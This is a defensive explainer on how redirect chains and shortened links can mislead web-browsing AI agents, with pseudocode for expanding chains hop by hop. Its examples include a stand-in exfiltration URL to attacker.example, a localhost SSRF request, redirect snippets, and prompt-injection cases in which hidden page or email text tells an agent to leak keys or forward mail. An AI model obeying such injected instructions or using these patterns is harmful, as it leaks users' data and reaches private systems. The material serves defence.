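# Checking redirect chains and shortened URLs before an automated agent follows them

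## Links, redirects and web-browsing agents

A redirect is an instruction from a web server or web page that sends the visitor to a different address from the one requested. Site owners routinely set up redirects when pages move, and link-shortening services depend on them. The address in a link and the page that finally opens can therefore belong to different sites, with several other addresses in between. The whole sequence, from the first link to the final page, is a redirect chain, and each step is a hop.

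People have clicked through redirect chains for decades, mostly without noticing, and software now does it for them. An AI agent is software in which a language model chooses actions, such as opening a web page, and tools carry them out. When an agent follows a link, it sends requests to servers that may be run by strangers, who then decide where the next request goes. Checking a chain means finding out where it leads, and deciding whether the agent may go there, before any damage happens.

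### The parts of a URL

A URL is the full address in a link. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which writes many of the internet's technical standards, fixed its format in a standard for the slightly wider class of identifiers called URIs. IETF (2005) divides an address into five components. Take `https://docs.example.com/guides/start?lang=en#install`:

| Part | In the example | What happens to it |
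|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Tells the client which protocol to use, here an encrypted one |
| Host | `docs.example.com` | Names the server; the client looks up its network address and repeats the name in the request |
| Path | `/guides/start` | Goes to the server |
| Query | `lang=en` | Goes to the server with the path |
| Fragment | `install` | Stays with the client |

"Client" here means whatever program makes the request, whether a browser or an agent's tool. The current standard for web requests, the IETF's *HTTP Semantics*, gives the opening of a request for `http://www.example.org/pub/WWW/`:

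```
GET /pub/WWW/ HTTP/1.1
Host: www.example.org
```

GET is the ordinary method for asking for a page. A query, if the URL had one, would follow the path on the first line. A fragment would appear nowhere, because the client removes it before sending anything and uses it locally, typically to scroll to a heading. (Code running in the page can still read it.)

The host is the most important part of a URL to check closely, and it is easy to misread. A URL may include a user name and an at-sign before the host, so `https://docs.example.com@attacker.example/` leads to `attacker.example`. The 2005 standard warns about user names crafted to look like a trusted domain. The host may also be a numeric address such as `192.168.0.10`, which belongs to a machine on a private network.

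Whoever writes a link can put almost any text in its path and query, including a second URL, which the IETF notes is a frequent use of the query. A request for `https://docs.example.com/go?to=https://attacker.example/` goes to `docs.example.com`. That server's operator decides how it handles the second URL, and can have it redirect the request there.

### One redirect, two requests

Wizard Zines' *http redirects*, a short explanatory comic, follows a browser that asks for a picture of a dog and ends up with a cat. The browser first sends:

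```
GET /dog.png HTTP/1.1
Host: examplecat.com
```

The server does not return a picture. Its response begins with a status code, a three-digit number that describes the outcome, and codes that start with 3 mean that the client has to do something further:

```
HTTP/1.1 301 Moved Permanently
Location: /cat.png
```

The Location header holds the new address. The browser makes a second request:

```
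GET /cat.png HTTP/1.1
Host: examplecat.com
```

This time the server returns `200 OK` and the content. The user sees only the cat and, if they look, a changed address bar.

MDN's *Location header*, from Mozilla's reference site for web developers, explains that the new address may be relative, such as `/cat.png`, or absolute. A relative address keeps the client on the same host, but an absolute one can name any host. In the comic's other case, `examplecat.com/panda` redirects to `pandas.com`, so the second request goes to a server not named in the original link. That server can then redirect the client again.

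Under the IETF's wording, a client "MAY" follow a Location header automatically, so doing so is optional. Most browsers and many programming libraries do, and the code that called them may receive only the last page.

An HTML page can also redirect a browser, either through a refresh tag that specifies another URL or through a script that loads one. The server returns an ordinary 200 response in these cases, and the redirect takes effect only if the client interprets the page.

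### How an agent opens a page

A language model produces text. It cannot send a request to a server, so another program has to do that for it. Anthropic, the company that makes the Claude models, describes the arrangement in its developer documentation. In Anthropic's *How tool use works* the developer specifies which tools exist and what inputs they take, and the model determines when to call them. The resulting cycle is the action loop:

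1. The application sends the model the user's message and a list of tools.
2. The model replies with a structured request, such as the name of a page-opening tool and a URL.
3. Ordinary code carries out the request.
4. The application sends the result back to the model along with the conversation so far.
5. The model asks for another tool, which restarts the cycle at the third step, or it stops, usually with a final answer.

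The code in the third step runs in different places depending on the tool. Anthropic runs its web fetch tool on its own servers, where several fetches can take place before the developer's application receives a response. With Anthropic's browser tool, the developer's application operates the browser. Where the code runs determines which network a request leaves from, and so which private machines it could reach.

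These two tools also represent the two main ways agents read the web. A simple fetcher takes a URL and returns text. The one described in Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* retrieves a web page or PDF and passes its text to the model with the URL and retrieval time. It does not support pages that build their content with JavaScript, so a JavaScript redirect should have no effect on it.

A full browser loads the page, runs its code and lets the model act on what appears. Anthropic's *Browser use tool* gives the model 27 operations by default, including `navigate`, `read_page` and `left_click`. In the documentation's example, the user asks how to get started with some software. The model calls `navigate` with the address `https://example.com/docs`, then calls `read_page` and receives a list of the page's links and buttons, each with a short label. It can then click the "Getting started" link by its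 label, `ref_2`. The click call contains no URL because the browser takes the address from the page.

Browsers make requests that neither the user nor the model individually asked for, because a page can load images, scripts and other files from any host. Developers accept the extra exposure because many sites do not work without these requests. OpenAI recommends that developers use web search for public information that needs no interaction, and offers browser tools for other tasks.

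### Three ways a link can do harm

The most familiar danger is a malicious page, which may imitate a login screen to collect passwords (phishing) or deliver malware, software that damages or takes over a computer. Agents can also encounter prompt injection, which is text in outside content that a language model treats as an instruction. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available*, which announces an agent that works inside the user's browser, gives the example of a person who asks the agent to draft replies to emails. One message contains a hidden instruction to forward the person's other emails to the attacker.

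Prompt injection works because the model receives everything, including the user's request and a stranger's web page, as one stream of text and has limited means of giving one part more authority than another. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) calls this "context flattening". The paper also distinguishes indirect injection, in which the user asked for the page that carries the instruction, from what it calls implicit injection, in which the system fetches a link preview without anyone asking and the instruction is in the page's title or description.

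How often such attacks succeed depends heavily on the agent. In tests by Lan and colleagues, an agent that used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, sent secrets to the attacker with a probability of about 0.89 over 480 runs. The setup favored the attacker because the secrets were visible to the model and the page text was unfiltered. Anthropic reports far lower figures for its models against attacks from professional testers. Before additional safeguards, attacks that reached the model succeeded 17.6% of the time against Claude Opus 4.5 and 3.8% against the later Opus 5. With those safeguards on, none succeeded against Opus 5 and 0.3% did against Claude Fable 5. The two sets of tests are not directly comparable, but together they suggest that a good current agent resists most known attacks and a weak one resists very few.

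A link can also lead to a private network address. Companies run many services, such as administration pages and databases, that only machines inside their network can reach. Some require no password because their owners assume that outsiders cannot connect. In server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attacker gets a server to make the connection for them. MDN's *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* gives the example of a website that fetches an image from any URL a visitor supplies. The attacker supplies `http://localhost:443/admin/org.png`. "Localhost" is every computer's name for itself, so the server fetches a file from its own administration area and passes it to the attacker.

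The forged request runs "with the server's privilege level", according to MITRE's *Server Side Request Forgery*, an entry in a public catalogue of attack patterns. An archived page from OWASP, a software-security foundation, also titled *Server Side Request Forgery*, lists internal databases and the metadata that cloud providers supply to their customers' machines among the targets. The attacker can use a redirect to get around a check on the supplied URL. MDN describes a harmless-looking public address that only redirects to localhost.

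SSRF exploits programs that request addresses supplied by other people, as an agent's page-opening tool does. Lan and colleagues point out that a sentence in a web page can be enough for an attack if it gets the model to make the request, so the attacker may not need to enter an address in a form field. They compare the agent to a "confused deputy", an old computer security term for a program that misuses its authority at the prompting of someone who has none.

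Opening a URL can also leak private data, even if the page is harmless and the address is public. The URL itself carries data to the server, and servers commonly log the URLs that clients request. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives the example `https://attacker.example/collect?data=`, with something private after the equals sign. If an attacker can get the model to add private text to this URL and open it, the attacker can read that text in the server's log. OpenAI adds that the user may never find out, because the request might happen in the background, as when an agent loads an image or previews a link.

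These harms occur at different moments. A malicious page does its harm through the response, so the agent's software can still block it after sending the request. Leaked data is exposed as soon as the request arrives. Requests to a private address can do harm at either point. The response may contain secrets, but a flood of requests can also overload an internal service, and the service's response time can reveal something about it. One harm can also lead to another. In the attack that Lan and colleagues tested, a page's hidden description contained an instruction for the agent to "verify connectivity" by opening a URL with the user's secret key in the query.

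### An agent compared with a person hovering over a link

A careful person who distrusts a link hovers over it and reads the address the browser displays. This check is weak because it shows only the first URL in the chain. But the person pauses to do it, knows something about the sender, and remembers what the real site's address looks like.

An agent may open a link seconds after reading it, then follow another from the page it reaches, with nobody watching. Anthropic's Chrome agent originally asked the user to approve every action. It can now act without asking, and an automatic classifier compares each action with the user's request.

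The Chrome agent uses the logins already in the user's browser, so a page that misleads it may gain the use of those accounts. The conversation can also contain private material, such as emails, documents or keys, all of which the model can use when it composes the next URL.

Agents often take links from text that nobody has checked. An agent may find a URL in an email, a search result or a comment on a page, next to an instruction to open it. Anthropic tells developers that Claude sometimes follows instructions in page content even when they conflict with the developer's own.

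### A short link in an email

Suppose Ruth, an office manager, has an agent that works in the browser on her office computer, where she is signed in to her email. Anthropic's *Claude gets its own browser in Cowork* mentions working through an inbox as a typical job for an agent with access to signed-in accounts, and cautions that its safeguards reduce the risk of prompt injection but do not eliminate it.

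An email that appears to come from a supplier reads: "Your revised invoice is ready. View it at `https://short.example/q7Xk`." Ruth asks the agent to summarise the message. The invoice seems to be the point of the email, so the model calls its `navigate` tool with the short link. The server at `short.example` looks up the code `q7Xk` and returns a redirect.

The same link in the email could lead to any of four results. If the email is genuine, the Location header points to `https://docs.example.com/invoices/1042` and the agent reads an invoice. The header could instead point to `https://docs.example.com.attacker.example/login`, a copy of the supplier's login page on the attacker's host, or to `http://192.168.0.10/admin`, a machine on the office network that Ruth's computer can reach but the attacker cannot. The chain could also end at a plausible invoice with an instruction in white text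 at the bottom to open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` followed by the subject lines of Ruth's latest emails.

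## How shortened links and other redirectors hide the destination

The short link in Ruth's email, `https://short.example/q7Xk`, consists of a host and a four-character code, neither of which identifies the supplier or the attacker. The shortening service stores the destination in its database, and the usual way to learn it is to query the service.

### How a shortening service works

Georgiev and Shmatikov (2016), in *Gone in Six Characters*, describe the usual design. For a genuine version of Ruth's link, it would work like this:

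1. The supplier submits a long URL, `https://docs.example.com/invoices/1042`, to the service.
2. The service picks an unused code, `q7Xk`, and stores the code and the URL together in its database.
3. The service returns the short link, which the supplier pastes into the email.
4. When a client opens the link, it sends `GET /q7Xk` to `short.example`.
5. The server looks up the code and returns a redirect, with the stored URL in the Location header.

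In *Short Path to Phishing*, Odgerel, Nosyk and colleagues studied the shortening services that appear in phishing reports and found that most redirect in the server's response. Others, especially those that earn money from advertisements, return an ordinary page that redirects with a refresh tag or a script. On one Danish service, the script waits 15 seconds before loading the destination.

Codes usually draw on 26 lowercase letters, 26 capitals and ten digits, which makes 62 choices for each place. Six places give:

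62 × 62 × 62 × 62 × 62 × 62 = 62⁶ = 56,800,235,584

That is about 56.8 billion codes. Four places, as in Ruth's link, give about 14.8 million.

A service may issue codes in sequence, choose them at random, or calculate them from the long URL with a hash function, which scrambles its input into a short value. A reader cannot work back from the code to the URL in any of these cases. A six-character code holds about 36 bits of information, enough for four letters of ordinary text, while a long URL can run to hundreds of characters.

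People mostly use short links for ordinary reasons. The links fit within a text message's 160 characters, don't break across lines in emails, and let businesses count clicks. Some services create more than 600 million links a month. Many companies have their own short domain, such as the *New York Times*'s `nyti.ms`, which runs on the servers of Bitly, a large link-shortening company. Some platforms give the writer no choice. By 2016, all links posted to Twitter passed through its `t.co` service, according to Trend Micro's *Are shortened URLs safe?* (2016).

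### Guessing the codes

The code in a shortened link hides the destination from someone who only reads the link, but it doesn't keep the destination secret, because anyone can send any code to the server and see where it leads. Georgiev and Shmatikov tested how often guessing works by sending random codes to two URL-shortening services and counting how many led to a stored URL.

| Codes | Number tried | Links found | Share in use |
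|---|---|---|---|
| Bitly, six characters | 100,000,000 | 42,229,055 | 42% |
| Bitly, seven characters, the first always 1 | 100,000,000 | 29,331,099 | 29% |
| Google Maps, five characters | 63,970,000 | 23,965,718 | 37.5% |

The six-character scan used 189 machines and covered 0.176% of the possible codes. Because the codes were random, the result should hold for the rest. The researchers estimated that scanning all of Bitly's codes would have cost about $36,700 in rented computing.

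Many of the links led to content their owners had meant to share with only a few people. The six-character sample contained 19,524 links to files or folders in Microsoft's cloud storage. For ethical reasons, Georgiev and Shmatikov did not open the files, but they found that anyone could write to folders in about 7% of the storage accounts they discovered. Map links gave directions between private homes and clinics.

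Google lengthened the codes on new map links to 11 or 12 characters within a week of hearing about the problem. Microsoft replied that sharing by short link "appears by design". Microsoft later removed the option to shorten links but said the research had played no role in the decision.

These figures are a decade old and do not describe either service today, but the arithmetic still applies. With 42% of six-character codes in use, an attacker needed about two guesses to find a live link. If the same links had been spread over ten-character codes, finding each one would have taken about 35 million guesses. At 42%, an agent that copied one character of a code wrongly would also have opened a stranger's link about two times in five, with no error message.

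### Who controls a short link after its creation

The person who creates a link often keeps control of it. CaptainDNS's *URL Shorteners* (2026) explains that some services let the creator change the destination later. The creator can use this to fix a typing error, or to replace a harmless page with a phishing page after someone has checked the link. Rebrandly sells links that expire on a set date, and Short.io sells links that stop working after a set number of clicks.

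Carr (2025), in *The 6 URL Shorteners You Didn't Know Were Helping Hackers*, a report for the email security company Cofense, lists other features of URL shorteners. `t.ly` can send visitors to different pages according to their browser and location. Other services can put a password in front of the destination. Nearly all of them give the link's creator statistics on who clicked, so a scammer can learn from a click that a person or a program is reading the mail.

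The company that runs a link-shortening service can disable a link. Odgerel and colleagues followed a sample of short links from phishing blocklists for up to a month each. Seven of the ten most abused services disabled more than 70% of their sampled links, typically in under 48 hours. Bitly disabled half of its sampled links within 30 minutes. However, the researchers measured from when a link reached a blocklist, so these times exclude the hours or days before anyone reported it.

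A few operators of link shorteners have no interest in disabling any links. Krebs on Security (2023) reported on one such service, which the security company Infoblox named "Prolific Puma". Infoblox's head of threat intelligence said her team had found no legitimate content behind its links.

Shortening services also close. According to Android Authority, Google launched its shortener, `goo.gl`, in 2009 and closed it to new links in 2018, but promised that existing links would keep working. In July 2024, Google announced that all of them would stop working after August 25, 2025 (Chandel and Babu (2024), in *Google URL Shortener links will no longer be available [updated]*). Google said that 99% of the links had no recent activity. From August 2024, it showed visitors to some links a warning page before the destination.

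In *We’re updating our plans for goo.gl links*, published on August 1, 2025, Google narrowed its planned shutdown to links that had shown no activity in late 2024. All other `goo.gl` links were to keep working, including those made by Google's own apps, such as Maps. An old `goo.gl` link may therefore be live or dead, and its text does not show which.

When a smaller link shortener closes, its domain may expire and somebody else can buy it. The buyer then receives every request for the old short links and can redirect them anywhere. CaptainDNS gives the hypothetical example of a company whose old social media post starts leading to a scam.

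### Preview pages

Several URL shorteners show the destination without sending the visitor there. According to Carr, adding a plus sign to a `t.ly` link opens a page with the destination and click statistics, and adding a hyphen to an `is.gd` link does much the same. TinyURL has a preview setting, which it stores in a browser cookie.

An agent's developer cannot rely on the features that link shorteners offer for inspecting a link, because each service has its own and can withdraw it. According to Phish Report, a site for people who investigate phishing, Bitly and TinyURL used to show click statistics to anyone who added a plus sign or a tilde to a short link, but now show them only to the link's creator.

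A preview also shows only the URL stored under the code. If that URL is another short link, the visitor sees the second link but not where it leads. Carr found such chains in real attacks, in which an `is.gd` link often led to a `goo.su` link and then to a malware download.

Some services show every visitor a preview and wait for them to click a button. This may help a person, but the software Odgerel and colleagues used to follow links could not get past these pages, or past the CAPTCHA tests that a few services use to keep out automated visitors.

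### Open redirects

An attacker does not need a shortening service if a respectable site will do the same job. An open redirect is a page that forwards visitors to whatever address the link supplies. Fastly's *Open redirects* gives this example:

`goodexample.com/redir.php?q=badexample.com`

Unlike a short link, this one contains its destination, `badexample.com`, but in the query, where few people look. Attackers often make it harder to read by writing punctuation as codes, so that `https://` becomes `https%3A%2F%2F`. Fastly points out that security training has made the problem worse by teaching people to check that a link starts with the right domain, which this one does.

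Open redirects usually begin as a convenience, such as counting clicks on outbound links or returning users to their previous page after they log in or out. The flaw is that they accept any destination address. Developers can fix this by allowing only a fixed list of destinations, but many don't. Fastly's researchers found one person's collection of more than 3,000 such links, apparently gathered to raise certain sites in search rankings. At least nine months after that person listed them, 23 still redirected to any address.

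Some redirectors are only partly open. *How often are redirects used in phishing in 2026?* (Kopriva, 2026) describes Google links that redirect only if they contain a valid token, a string that Google issues. These tokens last a long time and work from any address, so an attacker can obtain one and send the same link to thousands of people. They would be a good defense if each one worked only once or for one visitor. Kopriva also found attackers using similar links from Bing.

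### Tracking links and rewritten links

Search engines, advertisers and newsletter services routinely use redirects to count clicks. A newsletter service, for example, replaces each link in a message with one on its own host, records who opens it, and redirects the reader to the real page. The recipient sees a long string of characters on an unfamiliar or vaguely familiar domain, whether the sender is legitimate or malicious. Redirect links can also get past software filters, as a search engine's redirect link did in ChatGPT.

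Email security products rewrite links to protect the reader. Cloudflare's *Attackers abusing Proofpoint & Intermedia link wrapping to deliver phishing payloads* (2025) describes how Proofpoint changes a link to `http://malicioussite.com` into one that starts with `https://urldefense.proofpoint.com/` and carries the original address in its query. When the reader clicks, Proofpoint's server checks the original address against the threats known at that moment, and either blocks the visit or redirects the reader.

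The check fails if nobody has yet identified the site as malicious, and the rewritten link looks safer than the original. In June and July 2025, Cloudflare tracked attackers who broke into email accounts at organizations that used Proofpoint or Intermedia, a similar product. They sent malicious links from those accounts so that the product would rewrite them. Some attackers then put the rewritten links behind short links and spread them more widely. The victim's browser went from the shortener to Proofpoint, then through more redirects to a fake Microsoft login page.

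If Ruth's employer used a product like this, every link in her inbox would start with the same host, including the links in the genuine invoice and the fake one. Her agent would approve both if it trusted that host, but blocking the host would cut it off from every link in her email.

Shorteners are also difficult to block, because blocking `bit.ly` to stop one malicious link would disable millions of harmless ones. Odgerel and colleagues describe a legitimate European service that went offline for about a day in 2024 because the registry suspended its domain. Attackers benefit from this reluctance to block shorteners. They may also benefit from familiarity, since *Comprehensive List of User Deception Techniques in Emails* (2026) suggests that people may regard a known shortener more neutrally than a domain they have never seen.

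### How often malicious links use redirects

Published figures range from 1% to almost 90%, largely because they count different things. Several of the highest come from VIPRE, an email security company, but most readers see them through other outlets: News in the Channel's *2025 Phishing Trends*, emailexpert's *Cybercriminals Use Creative New Tactics to Evade Email Security* and KnowBe4's *Most Phishing Attacks Abuse Trusted Services* (2026).

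| Source | What it covers | Period | Finding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Odgerel and colleagues | 1.5 million URLs from three phishing blocklists | December 2023 to December 2024 | 1% were short links |
| Kopriva | Slightly more than 350 phishing emails | January to March 2026 | About 21% used a redirect of some kind |
| VIPRE, in News in the Channel | Ways of delivering phishing links | Second quarter of 2025 | 54% open redirects, 7% shorteners |
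| VIPRE, in emailexpert | Phishing campaigns | Third quarter of 2025 | 80% hijacked links or open redirects |
| VIPRE, in KnowBe4 | Phishing URLs | First quarter of 2026 | Over 89% "abused URLs" |

VIPRE's figures each cover a different category, so the steep rise they seem to show may not be real. KnowBe4 reports that just under 90% of attacks abused open redirects, but the VIPRE sentence it quotes is about "abused URLs", which may well be a broader group. The sample behind the 80% figure is also unclear. VIPRE's *Email Threat Trends Report Q3 2025* gives a total of 1.8 billion emails processed, but that is all the mail the company handled, and the 80% refers to phishing campaigns, a tiny fraction of it. CaptainDNS gives a figure of 48% of malicious links in 2025 and does not tie it to any particular study.

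Kopriva's sample is small, and he calls it far from statistically representative. It came from his own filters and spam traps and from messages sent to the security center he writes for. The monthly share fell from 32% in January to 16.5% in March, but the drop may mean little in a sample this small. He does specify what he counted, which includes open redirects, tracking links and a small share of shorteners.

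The blocklist figure of 1% probably understates how often people come across malicious short links, because a blocklist counts each URL once, however many people receive it, and some reports may list the final page instead of the link in the message. Even so, Kopriva, VIPRE's 2025 breakdown and the blocklists all suggest that shorteners account for a modest share of phishing links. They also suggest that developers will miss many phishing links if their agents unpack short links but ignore other redirectors.

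Text messages may be different, since space is tight. *An Overview of 7726 User Reports* (2025) analyzed 1.2 million reports that UK phone users made between March and July 2024, and counted 2,280 distinct `bit.ly` links and 1,094 TinyURL links among the scams. *Read This Paper to Get $50 Million* (2026) collected 31,288 URLs from scam messages posted on Reddit, and found shorteners in every category of scam, from fake jobs to unpaid tolls. About 71% of the URLs, and 90% of those from 2025, had never been checked with VirusTotal, a service that scans links with more than 70 security products.

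A redirect is not suspicious in itself. Çolhak, Demirkıran and colleagues (2026), in *PhiShark2026*, scanned 33,387 phishing pages and 34,115 pages that two screening services had cleared. Excluding pages on free hosting platforms, they saw a redirect on 87.7% of the harmless sites and 75.8% of the phishing sites. The redirect led to a different host on 23.3% of the harmless sites and 14.4% of the phishing sites. Many of the redirects were probably routine, such as a move from `http` to `https` or the addition of `www`. These would be common among the harmless sites because their addresses came from a list of domains. Even so, an agent that refused every redirect would have rejected a larger share of the harmless sites than of the phishing sites.

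## Expanding a redirect chain one hop at a time

A server that redirects a client has to give it the next address, so software can trace a chain by requesting each address in turn. A program that does this, called an expander, records each response without passing the page to the agent. Unlike an ordinary web client, it stops after every response.

### The algorithm

The expander first turns off automatic redirects so that it receives each response as the server sent it. It then reads the status code and the Location header, works out the next URL, records the hop and repeats.

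```
url  = the first link
hops = empty list
seen = { url without its fragment }

repeat:
    response = GET url, with automatic redirects off,
               a 5-second timeout and a size limit
    if the request failed:               stop, "error"
    if the status is not 301, 302, 303, 307 or 308,
       or there is no Location header:   stop, "end of chain"

    next = resolve Location against url
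    if next has no fragment:             copy the fragment of url
    add (url, status, next) to hops

    if next is not http or https:        stop, "unsupported address"
    if next, without fragment, is in seen:  stop, "loop"
    if hops has more than 10 entries:    stop, "too many hops"
    if 20 seconds have passed in total:  stop, "out of time"

    add next, without fragment, to seen
    url = next
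```

At the bottom of the loop, the expander has the next URL but has not yet contacted its server, so a developer can apply rules there about where the agent may go. Only the result "end of chain" means that the expander found a destination. The agent's software should treat any other result as a failed check, because the link's destination is still unknown.

This code has to run outside a web page because browsers hide the intermediate URLs in a redirect chain from scripts. Under the Fetch Standard, published by the WHATWG, a standards group run by the main browser makers, a script can have the browser follow redirects (the default), treat any redirect as an error, or stop at the first one. If the browser stops, it hides the status and the Location header from the script. If it follows the chain, it reveals only the last URL and whether there was a redirect. In *URLs of intermediary redirects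 are leakable in practice (same-origin)*, ukusormus quotes an editor of the standard explaining that a Location value can be about as sensitive as a login cookie that browsers keep from scripts.

### Working out the next address

*HTTP Semantics*, which the RFC Editor publishes as RFC 9110, tells clients to resolve a relative address against the URL they have just requested. Suppose an expander has requested `https://click.example/mail/88`. Four similar Location headers would send it to four different places:

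| Location header | Next URL |
|---|---|
| `https://docs.example.com/go/88` | `https://docs.example.com/go/88` |
| `/go/88` | `https://click.example/go/88` |
| `go/88` | `https://click.example/mail/go/88` |
| `//attacker.example/88` | `https://attacker.example/88` |

A redirect address that starts with two slashes is dangerous because it looks like a path on the same site but points to a new host. Developers can avoid misreading it as a path by using a standard URL library instead of joining the parts of the URL themselves.

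Fragments carry over from one hop to the next. If a client opens `http://www.example.org/index.html#larry` and the server redirects it to `http://www.example.net/index.html`, RFC 9110 requires the client to go to `http://www.example.net/index.html#larry`. An expander that drops fragments can therefore report a slightly different destination from the one a browser reaches, and code in the page on the new host may behave differently because of the fragment.

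### What the five redirect codes mean

The codes differ in whether the move is permanent and in what happens to the request method. The second difference affects requests such as POST, which clients use to submit data like a completed form.

| Status | Name | Meaning | What the client does after a POST |
|---|---|---|---|
| 301 | Moved Permanently | The page has a new permanent address | May switch to GET, and browsers do |
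| 302 | Found | The page is temporarily at another address | May switch to GET, and browsers do |
| 303 | See Other | Another page holds the response | Switches to GET |
| 307 | Temporary Redirect | The page is temporarily at another address | Sends the POST again |
| 308 | Permanent Redirect | The page has a new permanent address | Sends the POST again |

The redirect codes overlap because early browsers disagreed about how to handle 301 and 302. The designers of HTTP meant both codes to preserve the request method, but some browsers changed it to GET, and eventually most did. HTTP later gained 307 and 308 for sites that needed the original behavior. RFC 9110 leaves out the sentence that forbids changing the method after a 308. When a reader reported this on an IETF mailing list, one of the people responsible for the text agreed that it was a mistake.

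An expander can treat all five codes alike, because a GET request stays a GET request under each of them. An agent that fills in forms has to distinguish between them. If it submits a password to one site and the server returns a 307 or 308 pointing to another, a client that follows the redirect sends the password to the second site too.

The expander has to check both the status code and the Location header, because the header alone does not make a response a redirect. A server also sends a Location header with status 201, to give the address of something it has just created. Status 300 offers a choice of versions of a page. RFC 9110 allows a client to follow a 300 response automatically if it has a Location header, but many clients don't. The expander should handle 300 responses the same way the agent's own tool does, or it may stop a hop early.

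### HEAD or GET

An expander mostly needs the response headers, which it can request without the page itself by using HEAD instead of GET. RFC 9110 lists link testing among the uses of HEAD. The server should send the same headers for both methods, but may omit any that it works out only while generating the page. Some sites also reject HEAD requests or run different code for them.

SpamAssassin's link expander, documented in *DecodeShortURLs*, uses HEAD requests by default. Its developers had to add a setting for GET because some services, including Bitly, did not otherwise return the correct address for a blocked link.

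GET is probably the better default for an agent's expander, since the agent will use GET to open the page. GET transfers little extra data if the expander closes the connection once it has the headers of a redirect. The expander also has to use GET to detect redirects in the page itself.

RFC 9110 calls both methods "safe", meaning that the client is only asking to read something. Requests are only harmless if the site's developers follow that rule. The RFC warns about addresses such as `page?do=delete`, where an automated GET request could delete a page. It makes the site's owner responsible for preventing this, but an expander that opens every "unsubscribe" and "confirm" link in an inbox could still trigger actions the user didn't want. An expander should therefore follow only the links that the agent intends to open.

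### Loops and limits

Two URLs can redirect to each other forever. RFC 9110 says clients should detect such loops and intervene. An expander can detect a loop by comparing each new URL with those it has already requested. It should compare the whole URL, including the query, because some services redirect to the same path with an extra parameter before sending the visitor on.

Comparing each new URL with earlier ones in the chain misses loops in which the address keeps changing. RFC 9110 describes one in which the URL grows with every redirect until the server rejects it as too long. Comparison can also end a legitimate chain, because some sites set a cookie and then redirect the browser back to the same address, which now opens normally. The Fetch Standard counts redirects instead of comparing URLs, so a browser follows up to 20 and treats the next one as a network error.

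Other software uses different limits. An early HTTP standard recommended a maximum of 5. When Dumez (2017) asked the WHATWG to consider a number below 20, Chrome and Firefox had already adopted 20, while Apple's CFNetwork library had a fixed limit of 16. SpamAssassin's default is 10. Python's Requests library allows 30 redirects, and Go's standard HTTP client stops after 10 requests.

An attacker can exploit these differences. If the expander gives up after 10 redirects and the agent's browser after 20, the attacker can put the malicious page at the end of a chain of 12. The agent is safe only if its software refuses links that exceed the expander's limit. Few useful links are likely to need more than 10 redirects, so this rule should rarely block one.

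The expander also needs limits on time and size. With ten redirects and a 5-second timeout per request, it could make 11 requests and take 55 seconds, so the pseudocode has a separate time limit for the whole chain. A server can also send a Retry-After header, which gives the minimum time to wait before following the redirect. The size limit stops a server from keeping the expander busy with an endless page.

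### Ruth's link in four hops

Suppose the short link in Ruth's email leads to the fake login page, and the attacker has put a click-tracking service and an open redirect on the supplier's real site in between. The expander makes five requests and records four hops:

| Request | URL | Status | Next address | Known so far |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `https://short.example/q7Xk` | 301 | `https://click.example/mail/88` | The short link leads to a tracking service |
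| 2 | `https://click.example/mail/88` | 302 | `/go/88` | The next page is on the same host |
| 3 | `https://click.example/go/88` | 302 | `https://docs.example.com/go?to=https%3A%2F%2Fdocs.example.com.attacker.example%2Flogin` | The chain has reached the supplier's real host, but the query contains another URL |
| 4 | The `docs.example.com` address from request 3 | 302 | `https://docs.example.com.attacker.example/login` | The supplier's site has an open redirect, and the next host belongs to the attacker |
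| 5 | `https://docs.example.com.attacker.example/login` | 200 | None | The headers contain no further redirect |

An expander that stopped after the third response would have reported the supplier's genuine host. The fourth response gives the address of the fake login page before the expander has contacted that page's host. The fifth request would only show whether the chain continues, so a developer whose rules already exclude the fake page's host can skip that request.

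### Redirects that the headers do not show

The page at the end of Ruth's chain could still redirect a browser, with a refresh tag or a script:

```
<meta http-equiv="refresh" content="0; url=https://attacker.example/next">

<script>window.location = "https://attacker.example/next"</script>
```

The zero in the refresh tag, also called a meta refresh, is the number of seconds the browser waits before it loads the URL. An expander can download the page, look for the tag and treat its URL like one in a Location header, without running the page's code.

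JavaScript redirects are harder to handle. The SpamAssassin bug report *DecodeShortURLs should support meta refresh* suggests that searching the page for common patterns would probably catch them too. This would work for the line above, which contains the whole address, but not if the script assembled the address from pieces or fetched it from a server after the page loaded.

The reliable way to find out what a script does is to run it in a browser. This catches many more redirects, but it is slower and uses far more memory than sending a few requests. The browser also has to wait for an unknown length of time. The Danish shortener, for example, delays its redirect by 15 seconds, which is longer than SpamAssassin's 5-second timeout. The browser may also fail to get past pages that require a click or a CAPTCHA.

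A browser also exposes the expander to more risk because it runs untrusted code and loads images and scripts that reveal the visit to more servers. Developers should run the browser on an isolated machine, without the user's logins or access to the private network.

A browser normally follows header redirects automatically, so the developer has to retrieve the hops separately. The Fetch Standard supports this through WebDriver BiDi, a protocol that lets a program control and observe a browser. The browser reports each redirect response to that program but hides this information from scripts in the page.

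Whether an expander needs a browser depends on how the agent opens pages. If the agent uses a simple fetcher that doesn't run JavaScript, an expander that reads headers will find the same redirects, unless the fetcher also follows refresh tags, which the developer should check. If the agent uses a full browser, the expander can check the headers and the refresh tag first, then use a browser only for pages that look like intermediate steps, such as a nearly empty page or one on a known shortener's host.

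### How a spam filter expands short links

SpamAssassin is an open-source program that mail servers use to score incoming email. Its DecodeShortURLs plugin, new in version 4.0.0, finds the destinations of short links so that SpamAssassin can compare them with lists of known bad domains. The plugin's published code closely resembles the pseudocode above. It turns off automatic redirects, requests the short link, reads the Location header and adds the new URL to the list of links in the message.

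The plugin can also raise separate signals when a short link leads to another short link, when the chain loops back to an earlier address, and when the chain exceeds the maximum length. Because of a small gap in the code, the plugin stops without raising the loop signal if a link redirects straight back to itself.

Unlike the pseudocode, the plugin makes another request only if the next host is also a known shortener. SpamAssassin's *URL shortener rules* lists more than 200 entries, including `bit.ly`, `t.co`, `youtu.be` and `doi.org`, which redirects to academic papers. According to a note, contributors should add only services that they have checked by hand and that spammers could abuse, because others would cause unnecessary requests. The developers validated most of the list in May 2022 and added a few entries in 2023.

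The plugin saves resources by stopping at the first unlisted host, which also means it rarely contacts an attacker's own server. SURBL, which publishes lists of domains found in spam, argued in *An Open Letter To Operators Of Redirection Sites* that following redirects would take too many resources for most mail filters, especially when the redirects form chains.

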